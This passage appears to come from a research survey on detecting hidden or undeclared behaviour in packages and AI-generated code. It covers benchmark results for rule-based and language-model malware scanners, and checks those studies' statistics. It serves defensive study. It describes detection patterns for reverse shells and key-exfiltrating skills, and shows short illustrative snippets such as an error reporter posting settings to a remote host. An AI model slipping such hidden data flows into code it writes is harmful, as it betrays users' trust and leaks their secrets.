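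A function without imports can still send data out. The card function from the first section has no import line and runs no strings as code, but it mails card numbers to a stranger by calling a helper defined elsewhere. A certificate therefore requires every name the function uses to be either its own or on a short list of safe built-in operations. The list must exclude built-ins that load libraries, open files or run text as code. The scanner should also reject the internal attributes of ordinary objects, because Python programs can use them to reach other parts of the system.

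Even addition can run arbitrary code in Python, because the objects on either side of the plus sign can define their own version of it. The certificate for `running_total` therefore assumes that the caller passes ordinary numbers. It also covers only the function itself, and the caller can still send the result anywhere.

Such a check will reject plenty of harmless code, including anything that imports Python's math library unless that library is on the list. This is usually acceptable because a rejected function goes on to the next kind of examination.

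#### A call to a known network library

```python
import requests

def exchange_rate(currency):
    address = "https://api.example.com/rates/" + currency
    return requests.get(address).json()["rate"]
```

A scanner can determine from the code that this function can open a connection and will try to do so whenever it is called with a text argument, because the request is unconditional. The host is fixed, since the argument comes after it and can change only the rest of the address. The only data the function deliberately sends is its argument.

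The scanner can't determine which host will finally receive the request, because the server may redirect it and this library follows redirects by default. If the call were behind a complicated condition, the scanner might also be unable to determine whether it ever runs, and could report only that the code can open a connection. Limiting outgoing traffic at run time can address both problems.

None of this settles whether the call is unwanted. A user who asked for exchange rates would expect it.

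#### A string built at run time

```python
def keep_rows(rows, rule):
    return [row for row in rows if eval(rule)]
```

Suppose a function lets someone filter a table by typing a rule, such as one that keeps every row with a price below ten. If the program always passes the same fixed rule, the scanner can substitute that text for the variable and check it like any other code. If the rule comes from a user, a file or a server, the scanner can't determine what code will run and should report the result as "unknown".

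Here the obstacle is that part of the program is missing, and analysis can't supply it. In the earlier examples, which fall under Rice's theorem, the scanner has the whole program but still can't always predict its behaviour.

The function could instead use a small parser that accepts only column names, numbers and comparisons, which would make it possible to certify the function. A code generator can easily produce a second version, so a scan of generated code can require this change more often than a scan of a finished package, whose author may no longer be available.

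### A reference point for "hidden"

Whether a behaviour is hidden depends on what somebody knew or expected, which can't be determined from the program text alone. For example, Cohen describes a virus that compresses the programs it infects to save disk space, but asks the user's permission first. It is still a virus because it infects programs, but he does not count it as a Trojan horse.

Thomas and Francillon (2018), in *Backdoors*, define a backdoor as an intentional construct that compromises a system's expected security by giving access to privileged functions or information. It has four parts: an input source, a trigger, a payload that runs when the trigger fires, and the resulting privileged state. In a router they discuss, the web interface skipped the login for any browser that identified itself by a particular name. The network connection was the input source, the comparison with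 that name was the trigger, and the privileged state was being logged in as a legitimate user.

The word "expected" needs somebody to do the expecting. Thomas and Francillon describe a system as a set of states with conditions for moving between them, and then distinguish the developer's version, the actual one, and the one the user has in mind. (A fourth version is what an analyst reconstructs by taking the system apart.) Their categories depend on where a piece of functionality appears:

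| | Developer's version | Actual system | User's expectation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary privileged access | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Intentional backdoor | Yes | Yes | No |
| Deniable backdoor | Can't tell | Yes | No |
| Accidental vulnerability | No | Yes | No |

They treat a backdoor as intentional if the program contains an explicit path from the trigger to the payload, as the router's did. All eleven real backdoors in their main comparison were of this kind. A deniable backdoor looks like an ordinary bug, and they concede that nobody can distinguish it from an accident by technical evidence alone. Version histories can help because they may show who made a change and when, but interpreting them still takes human judgment.

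Zdziarski (2016), in *Backdoor*, proposes a test with three conditions, all of which must hold: intent, consent and access. Intent raises the same difficulty.

For generated code, the developer's column is hard to fill in, because a function can look the same whether or not an attacker planted its behaviour. A reviewer can still fill in the other two columns by examining the code and asking the user what they expected.

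The four-part definition also fits some of this behaviour badly. The card function mails every number it receives, so it has no special trigger, and the attacker never logs in to anything. A scan that looked only for a trigger leading to a privileged state could miss code that simply leaks data.

### Comparing code with its declared purpose

Several groups tried in 2026 to make the comparison precise, mostly for agent skills. *SkillProbe* (2026) compares the set of capabilities that a skill's documentation declares, D, with the set that its code implements, C. A capability is a pair of a resource and a level of access. If C contains everything in D and more, the skill has "shadow functions". The two sets can also match, D can contain everything in C and more, or each can contain something that the other lacks.

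Comparing sets can be too coarse. The user who wanted `authorize_card` asked for something that contacts a bank, so D would include sending data over the network. If the tool recorded the resource simply as "network", sending the card number to a stranger would add nothing new to C, and the function would pass. He and colleagues partly avoid this problem by looking for undeclared flows as well as undeclared operations. In one of their examples, a skill promises only to read files and run a fixed analysis, but it also reads a secret key and includes it in a request to an outside address. Reading the key is an undeclared operation, and the path from the key to the address is an undeclared flow.

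*SkillConsist* (2026) distinguishes three ways code can disagree with its declaration. The code can contradict a required statement, fail to implement one, or do something the declaration doesn't mention. For our purposes, failing to implement a statement is mostly a quality problem, while the other two can hide a leak. The definitions count only behaviour that using the skill can trigger and that affects something outside the package or goes back to the agent. This is sensible because dead code does no harm, but whether behaviour can be triggered is undecidable in general, so any tool that applies the definitions has to approximate.

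The approximation can still give proof in one direction. Shi and colleagues' condition, quoted in the first section, was that the actual effects should all be among the claimed ones. A scanner can't always compute E(actual), but it can often compute a larger set, E(possible), which includes every effect that the code might have. Then

E(actual) ⊆ E(possible) ⊆ E(claimed)

is enough to clear the code of undeclared effects. If E(possible) contains something outside E(claimed), the scanner still has to establish whether the effect really occurs. If it can, it should report it, and if it can't, the answer is "unknown".

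All this assumes that the declaration is the right standard. *SkillSpec* (2026) explicitly assumes that the declared intent faithfully reflects what the user wants. This assumption is safer for a request, which the user wrote, than for a skill from a stranger.

### When the request settles the matter

Suppose the request is "sort these names by surname". The names are already in the program, and sorting them requires no connection, file or secret. E(claimed) therefore contains no outside effects, and a function that contacts a server exceeds it on any reasonable reading, whatever the server's reputation. A sorting function can usually meet the conditions for a certificate, so if the scanner can't certify it, that is a reason to ask for a simpler version.

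The request can also show that a behavior in the code isn't hidden from the user, as it would with the copy for the fraud desk in the first section. This is true even when the request is harmful. A program that records every keystroke is dangerous, but a user who asked for one knows about the recording.

Now suppose the user asks for an app that "reports errors", and the code generator includes this:

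```python
def report_error(error, settings):
    requests.post("https://errors.example.com/report",
                  json={"message": str(error), "settings": settings})
```

A scanner can trace an error and the program's settings to an outside address, but it can't determine whether a user who asked for error reporting would object to sending them there. Reporting an error could mean showing it on the screen, writing it to a local file, or sending it to the developer or to a company that collects crash reports. The request also doesn't specify what the report should include. Settings often help explain a crash, but they may also contain passwords.

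People have trouble with this too. Two researchers in the study by He and colleagues read the same 120 skill descriptions, before looking at the code, and marked which of 11 categories of security-relevant behaviour each one stated. They gave identical answers for 108 descriptions, and for only 94 when they used 32 finer labels. Descriptions also often leave out details, and these omissions caused many of SkillScope's false alarms. In 24.3% of all the skills, the code was merely more specific than the description, more than twice the share in which the code went beyond it.

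One way to fill in a vague request is to look at what similar programs do. Gorla, Tavecchia and colleagues (2014) tried this on Android apps in *Checking App Behavior Against App Descriptions*, using a tool called CHABADA. They started with 22,521 free apps, used a statistical model to find 30 topics in the descriptions, such as weather or travel, and grouped the apps into 32 clusters with similar mixtures of topics. Within each cluster, the tool identified which sensitive functions (those that need the user's permission) the apps normally call, and ranked the apps by how far they departed from that norm.

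One researcher examined the five most unusual apps in each cluster, 160 in total. Of these, 42 (26%) acted against their users' interests without saying so, 20 (13%) did something unexplained but not clearly harmful, and 98 (61%) were harmless. A London restaurant guide stood out because it read the phone's account list, number and device identifier. It sent this information to an advertising service that the app's description never mentioned.

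In a second test, the researchers added 172 known malicious apps without training the tool on any malicious examples. It flagged 56% of them, along with 16% of the harmless apps. Comparing apps with similar descriptions helped, since the tool flagged only 24% of the malicious apps when the researchers treated all apps as one group, and 47% when they used the app store's own categories. But harmless apps outnumbered malicious ones by about 13 to 1, so almost four out of five flags were false alarms.

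Gorla and colleagues' tool also relied on program text to find calls, so it could miss code generated at run time. It could also count calls that never happen, because checking whether a program reaches a call is a form of the halting problem. To work around this, they counted a sensitive call only if the app had also requested the matching permission.

A scanner could likewise compare a generated function with others written for similar requests, but it would learn what is common, which may differ from what users want. Advertising libraries that collected personal data were so common in the cluster of apps about money that two poker games stood out for not collecting any. If code generators routinely wrote code that sent settings along with every error, `report_error` would look normal to the scanner.

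It is more reliable to ask the user about what the scan found, for example, "This function sends error messages and all your settings to errors.example.com. Is that what you want?" If the user replies that errors should go to a local file, the vague request becomes precise, and the outside connection now contradicts it.

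## Benchmarks of rule-based scanners

Asking the user about each finding works only if the scanner doesn't produce too many findings. PyPI had this problem with its own scanner. In February 2020 its developers added a check with four YARA rules, which looked for suspicious imports and function calls in `setup.py`, a file that runs when someone installs a package. Two years later the administrators switched it off. Vu, Newman and Meyers (2022), in *A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches*, asked people who knew the system what they needed from a scanner, then tested the check alongside two others.

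### What PyPI's staff wanted

The study's interviewees were two PyPI maintainers who had built or operated PyPI's malware check and an academic who studies malicious packages. The sample was small, but fewer than ten people worked on malware scanning at PyPI. The maintainers said the check raised so many false alarms that it had little or no value. An administrator was willing to spend about 20 minutes a week on malware reports, at about a minute each. PyPI was already removing about 20 malicious packages a week, so the real cases alone used up that time.

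Vu and colleagues report in their abstract that administrators find even a false positive rate of 0.01% too high. The administrators' detailed requirements are stricter, allowing at most 0.001% for a scanner that checks packages after publication and less for one that can block an upload. They would accept a scanner that misses most attacks, because many malicious packages have almost no downloads and they believed that a skilled attacker could always get past an automatic check. They only wanted help with frequent, low-effort attacks, and they wanted a verdict they could confirm quickly rather than a list of suspicious features.

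Security companies and independent researchers did most of the scanning of PyPI. They sorted through the false alarms themselves and reported what they found, partly for the publicity. A researcher doing this may tolerate a false positive rate of 15%. PyPI's administrators were wary of paying for reports because a reward might tempt someone to upload malware and then "find" it.

### Three scanners on 2,584 packages

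For the test, Vu and colleagues collected 168 malicious packages from two earlier research collections, 1,430 popular packages and 986 random ones. Besides PyPI's check, they ran OSS Detect Backdoor, a Microsoft tool that matches text patterns, and Bandit4Mal, a version of a Python security checker with rules for malware. This is the share of packages on which each tool raised at least one alert:

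| Files scanned and type of package | PyPI's check | OSS Detect Backdoor | Bandit4Mal |
|---|---|---|---|
| `setup.py` only, malicious | 58.9% | 50.6% | 66.7% |
| `setup.py` only, random | 14.9% | 33.1% | 70.2% |
| `setup.py` only, popular | 33.2% | 41.7% | 79.5% |
| All Python files, malicious | 85.7% | 85.1% | 90.5% |
| All Python files, random | 67.8% | 77.2% | 84.6% |
| All Python files, popular | 94.2% | 96.6% | 96.6% |

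The false positive rates range from 15% to 97%. When the tools scanned every Python file, all three flagged popular packages more often than malicious ones, so an alert was, if anything, weak evidence that a package was harmless. Package size probably explains much of this, because a single match anywhere was enough to flag a package. The popular packages averaged about 31,600 lines of code, the random ones 2,800 and the malicious ones 1,400.

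Requiring several alerts before flagging a package doesn't reliably separate malicious packages from harmless ones. PyPI's check never raised more than three alerts on a malicious `setup.py`, but it raised up to 45 on a harmless one. OSS Detect Backdoor raised 124,267 alerts on one popular package. The type of alert was more useful than the number. In `setup.py`, the rule for network access made up a larger share of the alerts on malicious packages than on harmless ones, while the rules for starting another program matched about equally often in all three groups of packages.

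### A larger benchmark

In 2026, Guo and colleagues tested the same three scanners on the benchmark they built for PyGuard. Its main test set has 2,363 malicious packages and 2,394 harmless ones chosen from the most downloaded on PyPI. They also tested GuardDog, Hercule and SAP. Hercule uses CodeQL to look for five kinds of behaviour. SAP is a set of three classifiers trained on labelled packages: a single decision tree, a random forest (many trees that vote), and an XGBoost model, which adds trees one at a time to correct the errors of the earlier ones.

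| Scanner | False alarms | False positive rate | Misses | Recall | Recall on newer packages |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bandit4Mal | 1,927 | 80.5% | 1,080 | 48.69% | 94.40% |
| OSSGadget (OSS Detect Backdoor) | 2,000 | 83.5% | 244 | 88.38% | 86.33% |
| PyPI's check | about 2,110 | about 88% | 17 | 99.19% | 88.00% |
| GuardDog | 141 | 5.9% | 101 | 94.42% | 68.12% |
| Hercule | 183 | 7.6% | 327 | 84.47% | 81.35% |
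| SAP, decision tree | 244 | 10.2% | 1,570 | 25.42% | 33.45% |
| SAP, random forest | 139 | 5.8% | 462 | 78.05% | 24.13% |
| SAP, XGBoost | 181 | 7.6% | 1,381 | 34.39% | 49.42% |

Some of the published percentages don't match the counts. In their text, Guo and colleagues give GuardDog a false positive rate of 4.30% and Bandit4Mal one of 71.01%. The rates in the table are instead the false alarms divided by the 2,394 harmless packages. (For PyPI's check, the number of false alarms comes from its published precision of 49.66%.)

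The published recall figures have a similar problem. GuardDog's 101 misses and 94.42% recall imply about 1,810 malicious packages, and the other tools' figures imply about 2,100, rather than the full 2,363. If GuardDog did scan all 2,363, its recall was 95.7%, which is too small a difference to change the comparison.

Bandit4Mal's recall of 48.69% is questionable because the same tool flagged 90.5% of malicious packages in the earlier benchmark and 94.40% of the newer ones here. Something may have gone wrong in this run. Hercule's false positive rate may be too low, because Guo and colleagues stopped it when a package took more than an hour and counted that package as harmless. This happened to 112 packages, 109 of which were harmless.

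GuardDog did much better than the older rule-based tools, with about a fourteenth as many false alarms as Bandit4Mal.

#### Rules behind the false alarms

Most of the false alarms came from rules that match ordinary code. Bandit4Mal's rule that reports any web address contributed to 1,682 of the tool's false alarms, about 88%. The addresses included links to project home pages and documentation. Basic file reads set off alerts in 56% of cases, and writes did in 40%.

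OSSGadget flagged 97% of packages for Linux commands and 72% for "data exfiltration" when they performed routine file operations. PyPI's check flagged 97% under a rule for code that manipulates other code, although many had only used standard Python imports.

GuardDog made a more interesting mistake. Its rule for running text as code caused 58% of its errors on the main set, often because of a common way of reading a package's version number:

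```python
exec(compile(open("version.py").read(), "version.py", "exec"))
```

This line does run code from outside the file, and a scanner that reports every `exec` it can't resolve will flag it. But `version.py` is in the same package, so the scanner could open it, find a single assignment and drop the alert. This would also work on generated code when the whole project is available.

### Loss of recall on newer packages

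GuardDog's recall fell from 94.42% on the main set to 68.12% on newer packages. Calculated from its misses and the official package totals, recall fell from 95.7% to 76.0%. Its false positive rate rose slightly, to 6.9%, and most false alarms now came from its rule for suspicious links.

For the newer set, Guo and colleagues took malicious packages from a different database and picked harmless ones at random from recent uploads. Some of the change in results may therefore be due to the choice of packages rather than their age. Still, the results show why relying on one benchmark is risky. The SAP random forest had the best recall of the three classifiers on the main set and the worst on the newer one. Hercule's recall held up, but its false positive rate rose to 28.4%.

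*How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026) covers a longer period and compares 11 tools on 6,420 malicious npm package versions and 7,288 popular harmless packages. The SAP decision tree detected 87.15% of malicious packages from 2021 but only 39.49% of those from 2023. The paper shares its lead author with the PyGuard study, so the two aren't fully independent.

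The researchers found that, overall, 80.3% of the malicious packages used no evasion technique. Obfuscation became less common between 2022 and 2023, and the average number of sensitive function calls in a malicious package fell from 12.5 in 2021 to 6.8 in 2023. Many newer packages ran only one shell command, which makes them hard for a classifier to detect because their statistics look like those of a small harmless program.

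GuardDog recovered to 91.42% on the most recent packages, which the researchers attribute to updated rules. But they also say they ran every tool with fixed settings throughout. If they used one recent version of GuardDog for all years, its maintainers may have written some rules after seeing the packages in the test. In that case, the recovery would show that people can repair a rule-based scanner after an attack, but not that the scanner would have caught the attack on the day it appeared.

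#### Newer comparisons

Across the whole npm set, GuardDog had a recall of 89.92% and a precision of 96.99%, which works out at a false positive rate of about 2.5%. OSSGadget had a similar recall, 91.56%, but flagged about 79% of the harmless packages, partly because it matched the names of download commands in README files and comments.

The npm comparison also included GENIE, a strict set of CodeQL queries by Gobbi and Kinder, which had 99.76% precision but only 46.14% recall.

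The benchmark may overstate the recall of both GuardDog and OSSGadget. To confirm that a package was malicious, three experts checked only the code that either tool had flagged. They removed 1,367 supposedly malicious versions this way, some of which may have contained attacks that both tools missed.

*One Detector Fits All* (Montaruli, Compagna and colleagues, 2025) reports a far lower recall for GuardDog, 6.63% at a false positive rate of 1%, on a Python data set with 3,190 malicious and 3,368 harmless packages. Even apart from the different data, this can be consistent with the higher figures, because GuardDog's usual settings gave a false positive rate of 5.9% in the PyGuard benchmark, and reducing that to 1% means ignoring most of its alerts. Recall figures should therefore be reported with their false positive rates.

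All three studies tested GuardDog before version 3, so their results may not apply to the current version.

### Precision at a realistic base rate

As the first section showed, a scanner's precision drops when malicious code is rare. If π is the share of releases that are malicious, R the recall and F the false positive rate, then

precision = πR / (πR + (1 − π)F).

Vu and colleagues report about 20,000 new releases a week on PyPI and about 20 removals, which suggests a share of 0.1%. The true share is higher if some malware escapes notice. Suppose a scanner has a recall of 90%, so that it finds 18 of the 20, and that each alert takes a minute to review:

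| False positive rate | False alerts a week | Precision | Weekly review time |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 999 | 1.8% | 17 hours |
| 1% | 200 | 8.3% | 3.6 hours |
| 0.1% | 20 | 47% | 38 minutes |
| 0.01% | 2 | 90% | 20 minutes |
| 0.001% | 0.2 | 99% | 18 minutes |

GuardDog's false positive rate on the main PyGuard set would put it slightly above the first row. Although its precision in the benchmark was 92.38%, it would produce more than 60 false alerts for every real one on PyPI. At a false positive rate of 0.01%, reviewing the scanner's alerts would take up all of the administrators' 20 minutes, leaving no time for reports from outside researchers.

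These results depend on the assumed share of malicious releases. If that share were 1%, precision at a 1% false positive rate would be 48% instead of 8.3%.

Montaruli and colleagues provide a check with real data. They collected 91,949 releases from PyPI over 37 days in 2025, of which 216 were malicious (0.23%), and scanned them with an XGBoost classifier that extends the SAP features. They could set it to different false positive rates:

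| Maximum false positive rate | Malicious releases found | False alerts | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.05% | 77 | 35 | 68.75% |
| 0.1% | 92 | 81 | 53.18% |
| 1% | 180 | 781 | 18.73% |
| 10% | 196 | 9,152 | 2.10% |
| 30% | 208 | 27,478 | 0.75% |

The total of 216 includes only malware that public databases listed or that the researchers confirmed after a detector had flagged it. Any unnoticed malware would lower the recall. Even so, the results show how much a laboratory benchmark can overstate a scanner's recall. An earlier version of the classifier found 95% of malicious packages in the standard data set at a false positive rate of 1%, but only about 69% of those in an 80-day stream from PyPI.

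### Choosing a threshold

Overall precision doesn't show how many false alerts come with each additional detection. In the 37-day stream, raising the limit from 0.1% to 1% caught 88 more malicious releases but added 700 false alerts, or about 8 per release. Raising it from 1% to 10% caught only 16 more, with about 520 additional false alerts for each. If each alert takes a minute to review, finding one more malicious release in that range takes nearly nine hours.

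The first step might be worthwhile for a registry with enough staff, but the second rarely would be. Montaruli and colleagues set their scanner to a 0.1% false-positive rate for registries, which produced about two false alerts a day.

They set the false positive rate at 10% for a large software company, which only had to check the packages it used. Those 584 packages had 1,596 releases over the same 37 days, and the scanner raised 46 false alerts, or 1.24 a day. The actual false positive rate was 2.9%, well below the 10% setting. None of the packages was attacked during the test, so it measured how often the scanner raised false alerts but couldn't show whether it would catch an attack.

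In principle, an alert is worth reviewing if

probability that it is real × cost of a missed attack > cost of the review.

If a stolen password takes a team 40 hours to deal with, that is 2,400 times as long as a one-minute review, so the team should review alerts even if only one in 2,000 is real. The same reasoning might justify more reviews at a registry, since one malicious package can reach many people. But a registry's volunteers have limited time, so its threshold depends mainly on how many alerts they can handle.

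If a team's coding agent writes 200 functions a week, a scanner with a 5% false positive rate would raise about ten false alerts a week, which is manageable. Over a year, that adds up to about 520 false alerts and, if one function in 10,000 hides something (a rate assumed for illustration), perhaps one real one. Reviewing every alert may be worthwhile, but reviewers will struggle to stay attentive after the first few hundred.

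The team has an advantage over PyPI's administrators because the person who reviews an alert can be the one who asked for the code, and will often know at once whether an address belongs there. However, if the agent writes thousands of functions a day, the team will get as many alerts as a registry and will need a stricter threshold.

Adding a second scanner also changes the threshold for flagging a package. In the npm study, Guo and colleagues combined GuardDog with Packj, which flags any package that calls one of 56 sensitive functions. Flagging a package if either tool did caught 665 more malicious versions than GuardDog alone but added 6,015 false alarms. Requiring both tools to agree gave a precision of 97.39% and a recall of 89.07%, close to GuardDog's own results. A second scanner is most useful if it makes different mistakes and raises few false alarms.

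### From packages to single functions

These recall figures probably don't apply to generated code, partly because of the duplication described in the first section. Montaruli and colleagues' scanner found 92 malicious packages at the 0.1% setting, but these formed only 22 campaigns when grouped by shared code.

Scanners also often rely on features that a generated function lacks. In the npm study, two of GuardDog's 22 rules produced over 90% of its detections. One flags suspicious install commands, which a single function doesn't have. The other flags suspicious links and caused many of GuardDog's false alarms on newer Python packages. GuardDog detected just 7% of malicious code that builds and runs other code.

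The SAP classifiers are even less suitable, because 65% of their features count files by type. For a single function, nearly all of these counts would be zero.

Recent PyPI malware may resemble AI-generated code somewhat more closely. Of the 92 packages, 38 had their malicious code in ordinary source files, 35 in `setup.py`, and 19 in the file that runs on import.

The false positive rates are also uncertain and could be too high or too low. Guo and colleagues chose popular packages as their harmless examples partly because these set off more false alarms than random ones, which makes the test harder. A 20-line function also has far fewer places for an accidental match than a 30,000-line project. But a short program that downloads a file or runs a command contains little besides the operation that scanners look for.

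*MalGuard* (2025) describes a detector that scanned 64,348 PyPI uploads and flagged 144, of which 113 were malicious (78% precision). Of the 31 false alarms, 25 were small test demos that made web requests and started other programs but did no harm, and the other six were pranks. Short demos are probably closer to generated code than anything else in these benchmarks, so scanners might raise similar false alarms on generated code.

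A team can measure the false positive rate on its own code by scanning functions that someone has already reviewed. If the true rate is F, the chance of seeing no false alerts in *n* independent harmless functions is (1 − F)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives an upper limit of about 3/*n* for F, with 95% confidence. A clean result on 300 functions therefore suggests a rate below 1%, which is good enough for the team in the example. Showing that a scanner meets PyPI's limit of 0.001% would take about 300,000 harmless packages with no false alerts, far more than any of these benchmarks contain. Measuring recall is harder because the team would need a varied set of generated functions known to hide something.

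## Tests of language models as code reviewers

Most of the false alarms in those benchmarks came from rules that matched an ordinary operation without regard to its purpose. In the card function from the first section, one line asks the bank about the card and another mails the card number to an outside address. A rule about outside contact would treat the two lines alike. A language model can use the function's name and comment to infer that it checks a card, and that asking the bank serves this purpose while mailing the number doesn't.

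A model can also make errors that a rule can't. It may report behaviour that isn't in the code, identify a real problem and then dismiss it, or give a different answer when asked again. Text in the code, such as a comment or a string, can also mislead it.

### How PyGuard reaches a verdict

PyGuard, the detector that Guo and colleagues built for Python packages, gives its language model patterns and past cases to work from. To collect them, the researchers ran four rule-based scanners over 18,137 packages and got 956,131 distinct flagged positions. For each position, OpenAI's GPT-4.1 extracted where the values in the flagged call come from and which conditions and other calls lead to it. This produced 7,458 malicious snippets and 5,813 harmless ones that a scanner had wrongly flagged. The labels for these snippets came from the data set rather than from GPT-4.1.

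The model translated the snippets into lists of named actions. The researchers then searched these lists for recurring subsequences and found 116,007 patterns, which they cut to 304. Of these, 278 are decisive, meaning each occurred only in malicious code or only in harmless code. One decisive pattern opens a connection to another machine and then redirects the program's input, output and error messages to it, which gives whoever is at the other end a command line.

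The other 26 patterns occurred in both kinds of code and need judgement. For these, the model compared malicious and harmless examples and wrote down what separates them. One such rule might be that encoding system files is suspicious but encoding a user's own documents isn't. (Guo and colleagues required these patterns to be at least 90% one-sided, but then describe 11 of the 26 as only 50% to 80% one-sided, so some are weak evidence.)

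PyGuard examines a new package file by file:

1. The model finds the sensitive calls in a file and extracts their context.
2. It translates the calls into named actions, in order. For `gmgeoip`, the package that sends off the list of user accounts, these would be roughly "read a file, encode it, send it in a web request".
3. PyGuard looks for decisive patterns in the list, allowing other actions in between. A malicious pattern settles the matter, even if a harmless one matches too. If only harmless patterns match, the file passes.
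4. If no decisive pattern matches, PyGuard retrieves similar cases. It compares embeddings, which are lists of numbers that a model computes so that similar texts get similar numbers. It picks the five closest malicious and five closest harmless cases by their actions, and does the same again by their code.
5. The model receives the code, its actions, any matching pattern with its rule, and the retrieved cases. It returns a verdict, a confidence score and an explanation.

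One flagged file is enough to flag the package.

On the main test set, decisive patterns alone identified 1,763 malicious packages, so most detections never reached the last step. The model's judgement mattered more for harmless packages. It reviewed 873 that matched one of the 26 uncertain patterns and cleared nearly all of them.

### PyGuard against simpler uses of a model

Guo and colleagues compared PyGuard with GPT-4.1, which read the code without any patterns or cases, and with SocketAI, which makes a model review its own work. Zahan, Burckhardt and colleagues (2024) describe SocketAI's method in *Leveraging Large Language Models to Detect npm Malicious Packages*. The model first writes several independent reports on a file, listing sources, sinks and the paths between them. It then criticises the reports, picks the best one and improves it. Each report includes a malware score from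 0 to 1, and a package counts as malicious if any file scores above 0.5.

In the original test on 5,115 small npm packages, SocketAI with GPT-4 raised 3 false alarms and missed 90 malicious packages. With the older GPT-3.5, it raised 195 false alarms, and the researchers attributed 173 of them to the model making things up. Many of the files that triggered these 173 alarms were empty or nearly empty. One contained only the words "place holder", and the model reported that the code was probably collecting system information and sending it to an outside server.

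Guo and colleagues ran SocketAI with newer models, GPT-4.1 and the small GPT-4.1-nano, on Python packages:

| Test set | Reviewer | False alarms | False positive rate | Misses | Published recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Main | GPT-4.1 alone | 115 | 4.8% | 34 | 98.38% |
| Main | SocketAI | 161 | 6.7% | 250 | 88.12% |
| Main | PyGuard | 2 | 0.08% | 19 | 99.08% |
| Newer | GPT-4.1 alone | about 30 | 3.0% | 233 | 78.76% |
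| Newer | SocketAI | 153 | 15.3% | 166 | 80.65% |
| Newer | PyGuard | 5 | 0.5% | 49 | 94.14% |
| Obfuscated | GPT-4.1 alone | 637 | 62.5% | 13 | 98.75% |
| Obfuscated | SocketAI | 198 | 19.4% | 131 | 87.42% |
| Obfuscated | PyGuard | 25 | 2.5% | 10 | 99.02% |

The false positive rates are calculated as in the previous section, and the figure of about 30 comes from the published precision.

SocketAI did much worse here than in its original test, where its false positive rate was about 0.1%. The models and the programming language were different, but package size may matter more, because each extra file is another chance of a false alarm. Zahan and colleagues had favoured packages with at most 25 files, while the harmless packages in the main set here were among the most popular on PyPI.

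SocketAI's self-criticism also had limited effect. Zahan and colleagues found that successive reports were often identical and repeated the same mistakes. In one case the model's output described the code collecting sensitive information and sending it away, but the score it assigned was 0.4, below the threshold.

For the newer set, the published percentages imply about 2,100 packages for both GPT-4.1 and SocketAI, but 1,097 malicious ones for GPT-4.1 and only about 860 for SocketAI. PyGuard's figures imply about 840 malicious packages. The researchers seem to have counted about 250 packages as malicious in the GPT-4.1 test and as harmless in the others. That could account for most of the 233 malicious packages that GPT-4.1 supposedly missed, so its apparent loss of recall on newer packages may not be real.

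PyGuard's advantage doesn't seem to come from a stronger model. It raised 9 false alarms and missed 13 packages on the main set when it used the smaller GPT-4.1-mini instead of GPT-4.1. The open model DeepSeek-V3 did slightly better than GPT-4.1 on the newer set. However, PyGuard differs from GPT-4.1 alone in several ways, including the extracted context, the translation into actions and the retrieved cases, so the comparison doesn't show how much each one helps.

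Guo and colleagues also used PyGuard's patterns and cases to review the alerts of older scanners. OSSGadget's false alarms on the main set fell from 2,000 to 192, while its recall fell only slightly, from 88.38% to 87.57%. This suggests that costs could be reduced by having a rule-based scanner flag code and a model review only the flagged parts. Zahan and colleagues measured the savings for SocketAI. When CodeQL chose the files, GPT-4 read 4,146 instead of 18,754, and the cost fell from about $2,014 to $482. However, the scanner's rules should flag code broadly, because the model can't recover anything the scanner misses.

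### Obfuscated code that does no harm

Guo and colleagues made the obfuscated set by running 1,019 harmless and 1,050 malicious packages through a tool that renames variables, rearranges the control flow and encodes strings. The programs behaved as before, but their code was much harder to read.

GPT-4.1 alone flagged 637 of the 1,019 harmless packages in the obfuscated set. Its recall stayed very high, but it flagged malicious packages only 1.6 times as often as harmless ones, compared with about 20 times as often on the main set (98.4% against 4.8%). If one release in 1,000 is malicious, an alert with the lower ratio raises the probability to only about one in 630, which hardly justifies a reviewer's time.

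In effect, the model treated obfuscated code as malicious. That is a poor rule for a package registry, where obfuscated code is often harmless, but it would be less of a mistake for a function that a code generator has just written. Even then, reporting the code as unreadable is more accurate than reporting it as malicious, and the natural response is to ask for a readable version.

SocketAI's false positive rate on this set was about a third of GPT-4.1's. SocketAI's original instructions tell the model not to report minified code as obfuscated, which may have helped keep the rate low.

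PyGuard did far better because it checks the order of operations, and Intensio, the tool that produced all the obfuscated packages, leaves that order intact. A different tool might hide which library functions the program calls until it runs, and the model would then have trouble naming the actions. PyGuard's 2.5% false positive rate covers only one kind of obfuscation, and it is still about 30 times the rate on the main set.

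### Copies on both sides of the split

Guo and colleagues used 80% of their data to find the patterns and kept 20% for the main test. This test is fair only if the two parts are really different, which there is reason to doubt.

Their malicious collection contains 9,552 packages in 10,906 versions. The researchers seem to have split it by version, because the two parts contain 8,543 and 2,363 malicious items, which add up to 10,906. One version of a package could therefore help create a pattern and another could test it. Different packages also often share code, and the paper doesn't mention keeping copies in the same part.

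Suppose a snippet appears in *k* items and each goes into the larger part with probability 0.8. The chance that a test item has at least one copy there is

1 − 0.2^(*k* − 1).

This is 80% for a snippet that appears twice and over 99% for one that appears four times. On average, each distinct snippet in the larger part appeared in nearly four items, though the number varies widely because a few large batches can account for many of the copies. Much of PyGuard's recall on the main set may therefore reflect code it had effectively seen before.

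The problem is smaller on the harmless side because the researchers took one version of each package. The newer set is a better test of recall, since its malicious packages came from a different database. Guo and colleagues also say GPT-4.1 could not have seen the newer set's packages in training, because they collected them through July 2024 and the model's training data ended in June. But a collection that runs through July can include packages from before June, and attackers often reuse old code.

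### The 19 misses

PyGuard missed 19 malicious packages on the main set, and Guo and colleagues explain all of them:

| What the package did | Misses | What might catch it |
|---|---|---|
| Imported a malicious dependency | 8 | A check of every imported package |
| Fetched and installed code from a remote repository at run time | 6 | A rule against such downloads, or a run without network access |
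| Kept its payload in a file that wasn't Python | 5 | A scan of the other files |

In each case the harmful part was outside the Python code that PyGuard reads, so a better model given the same text would make no difference.

The first two cases can easily occur in generated code. Someone has to look up any imported library, because the function's text doesn't show whether the library is safe. A download at run time is at least visible in the code, and a reviewer that can't see what the program will install should answer "unknown" instead of passing the code.

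### PyGuard on live uploads

From March to June 2024, Guo and colleagues ran PyGuard on 8,249 new PyPI packages, and it flagged 233. They checked each flagged package by hand and reported 219. PyPI's staff confirmed and removed all 219.

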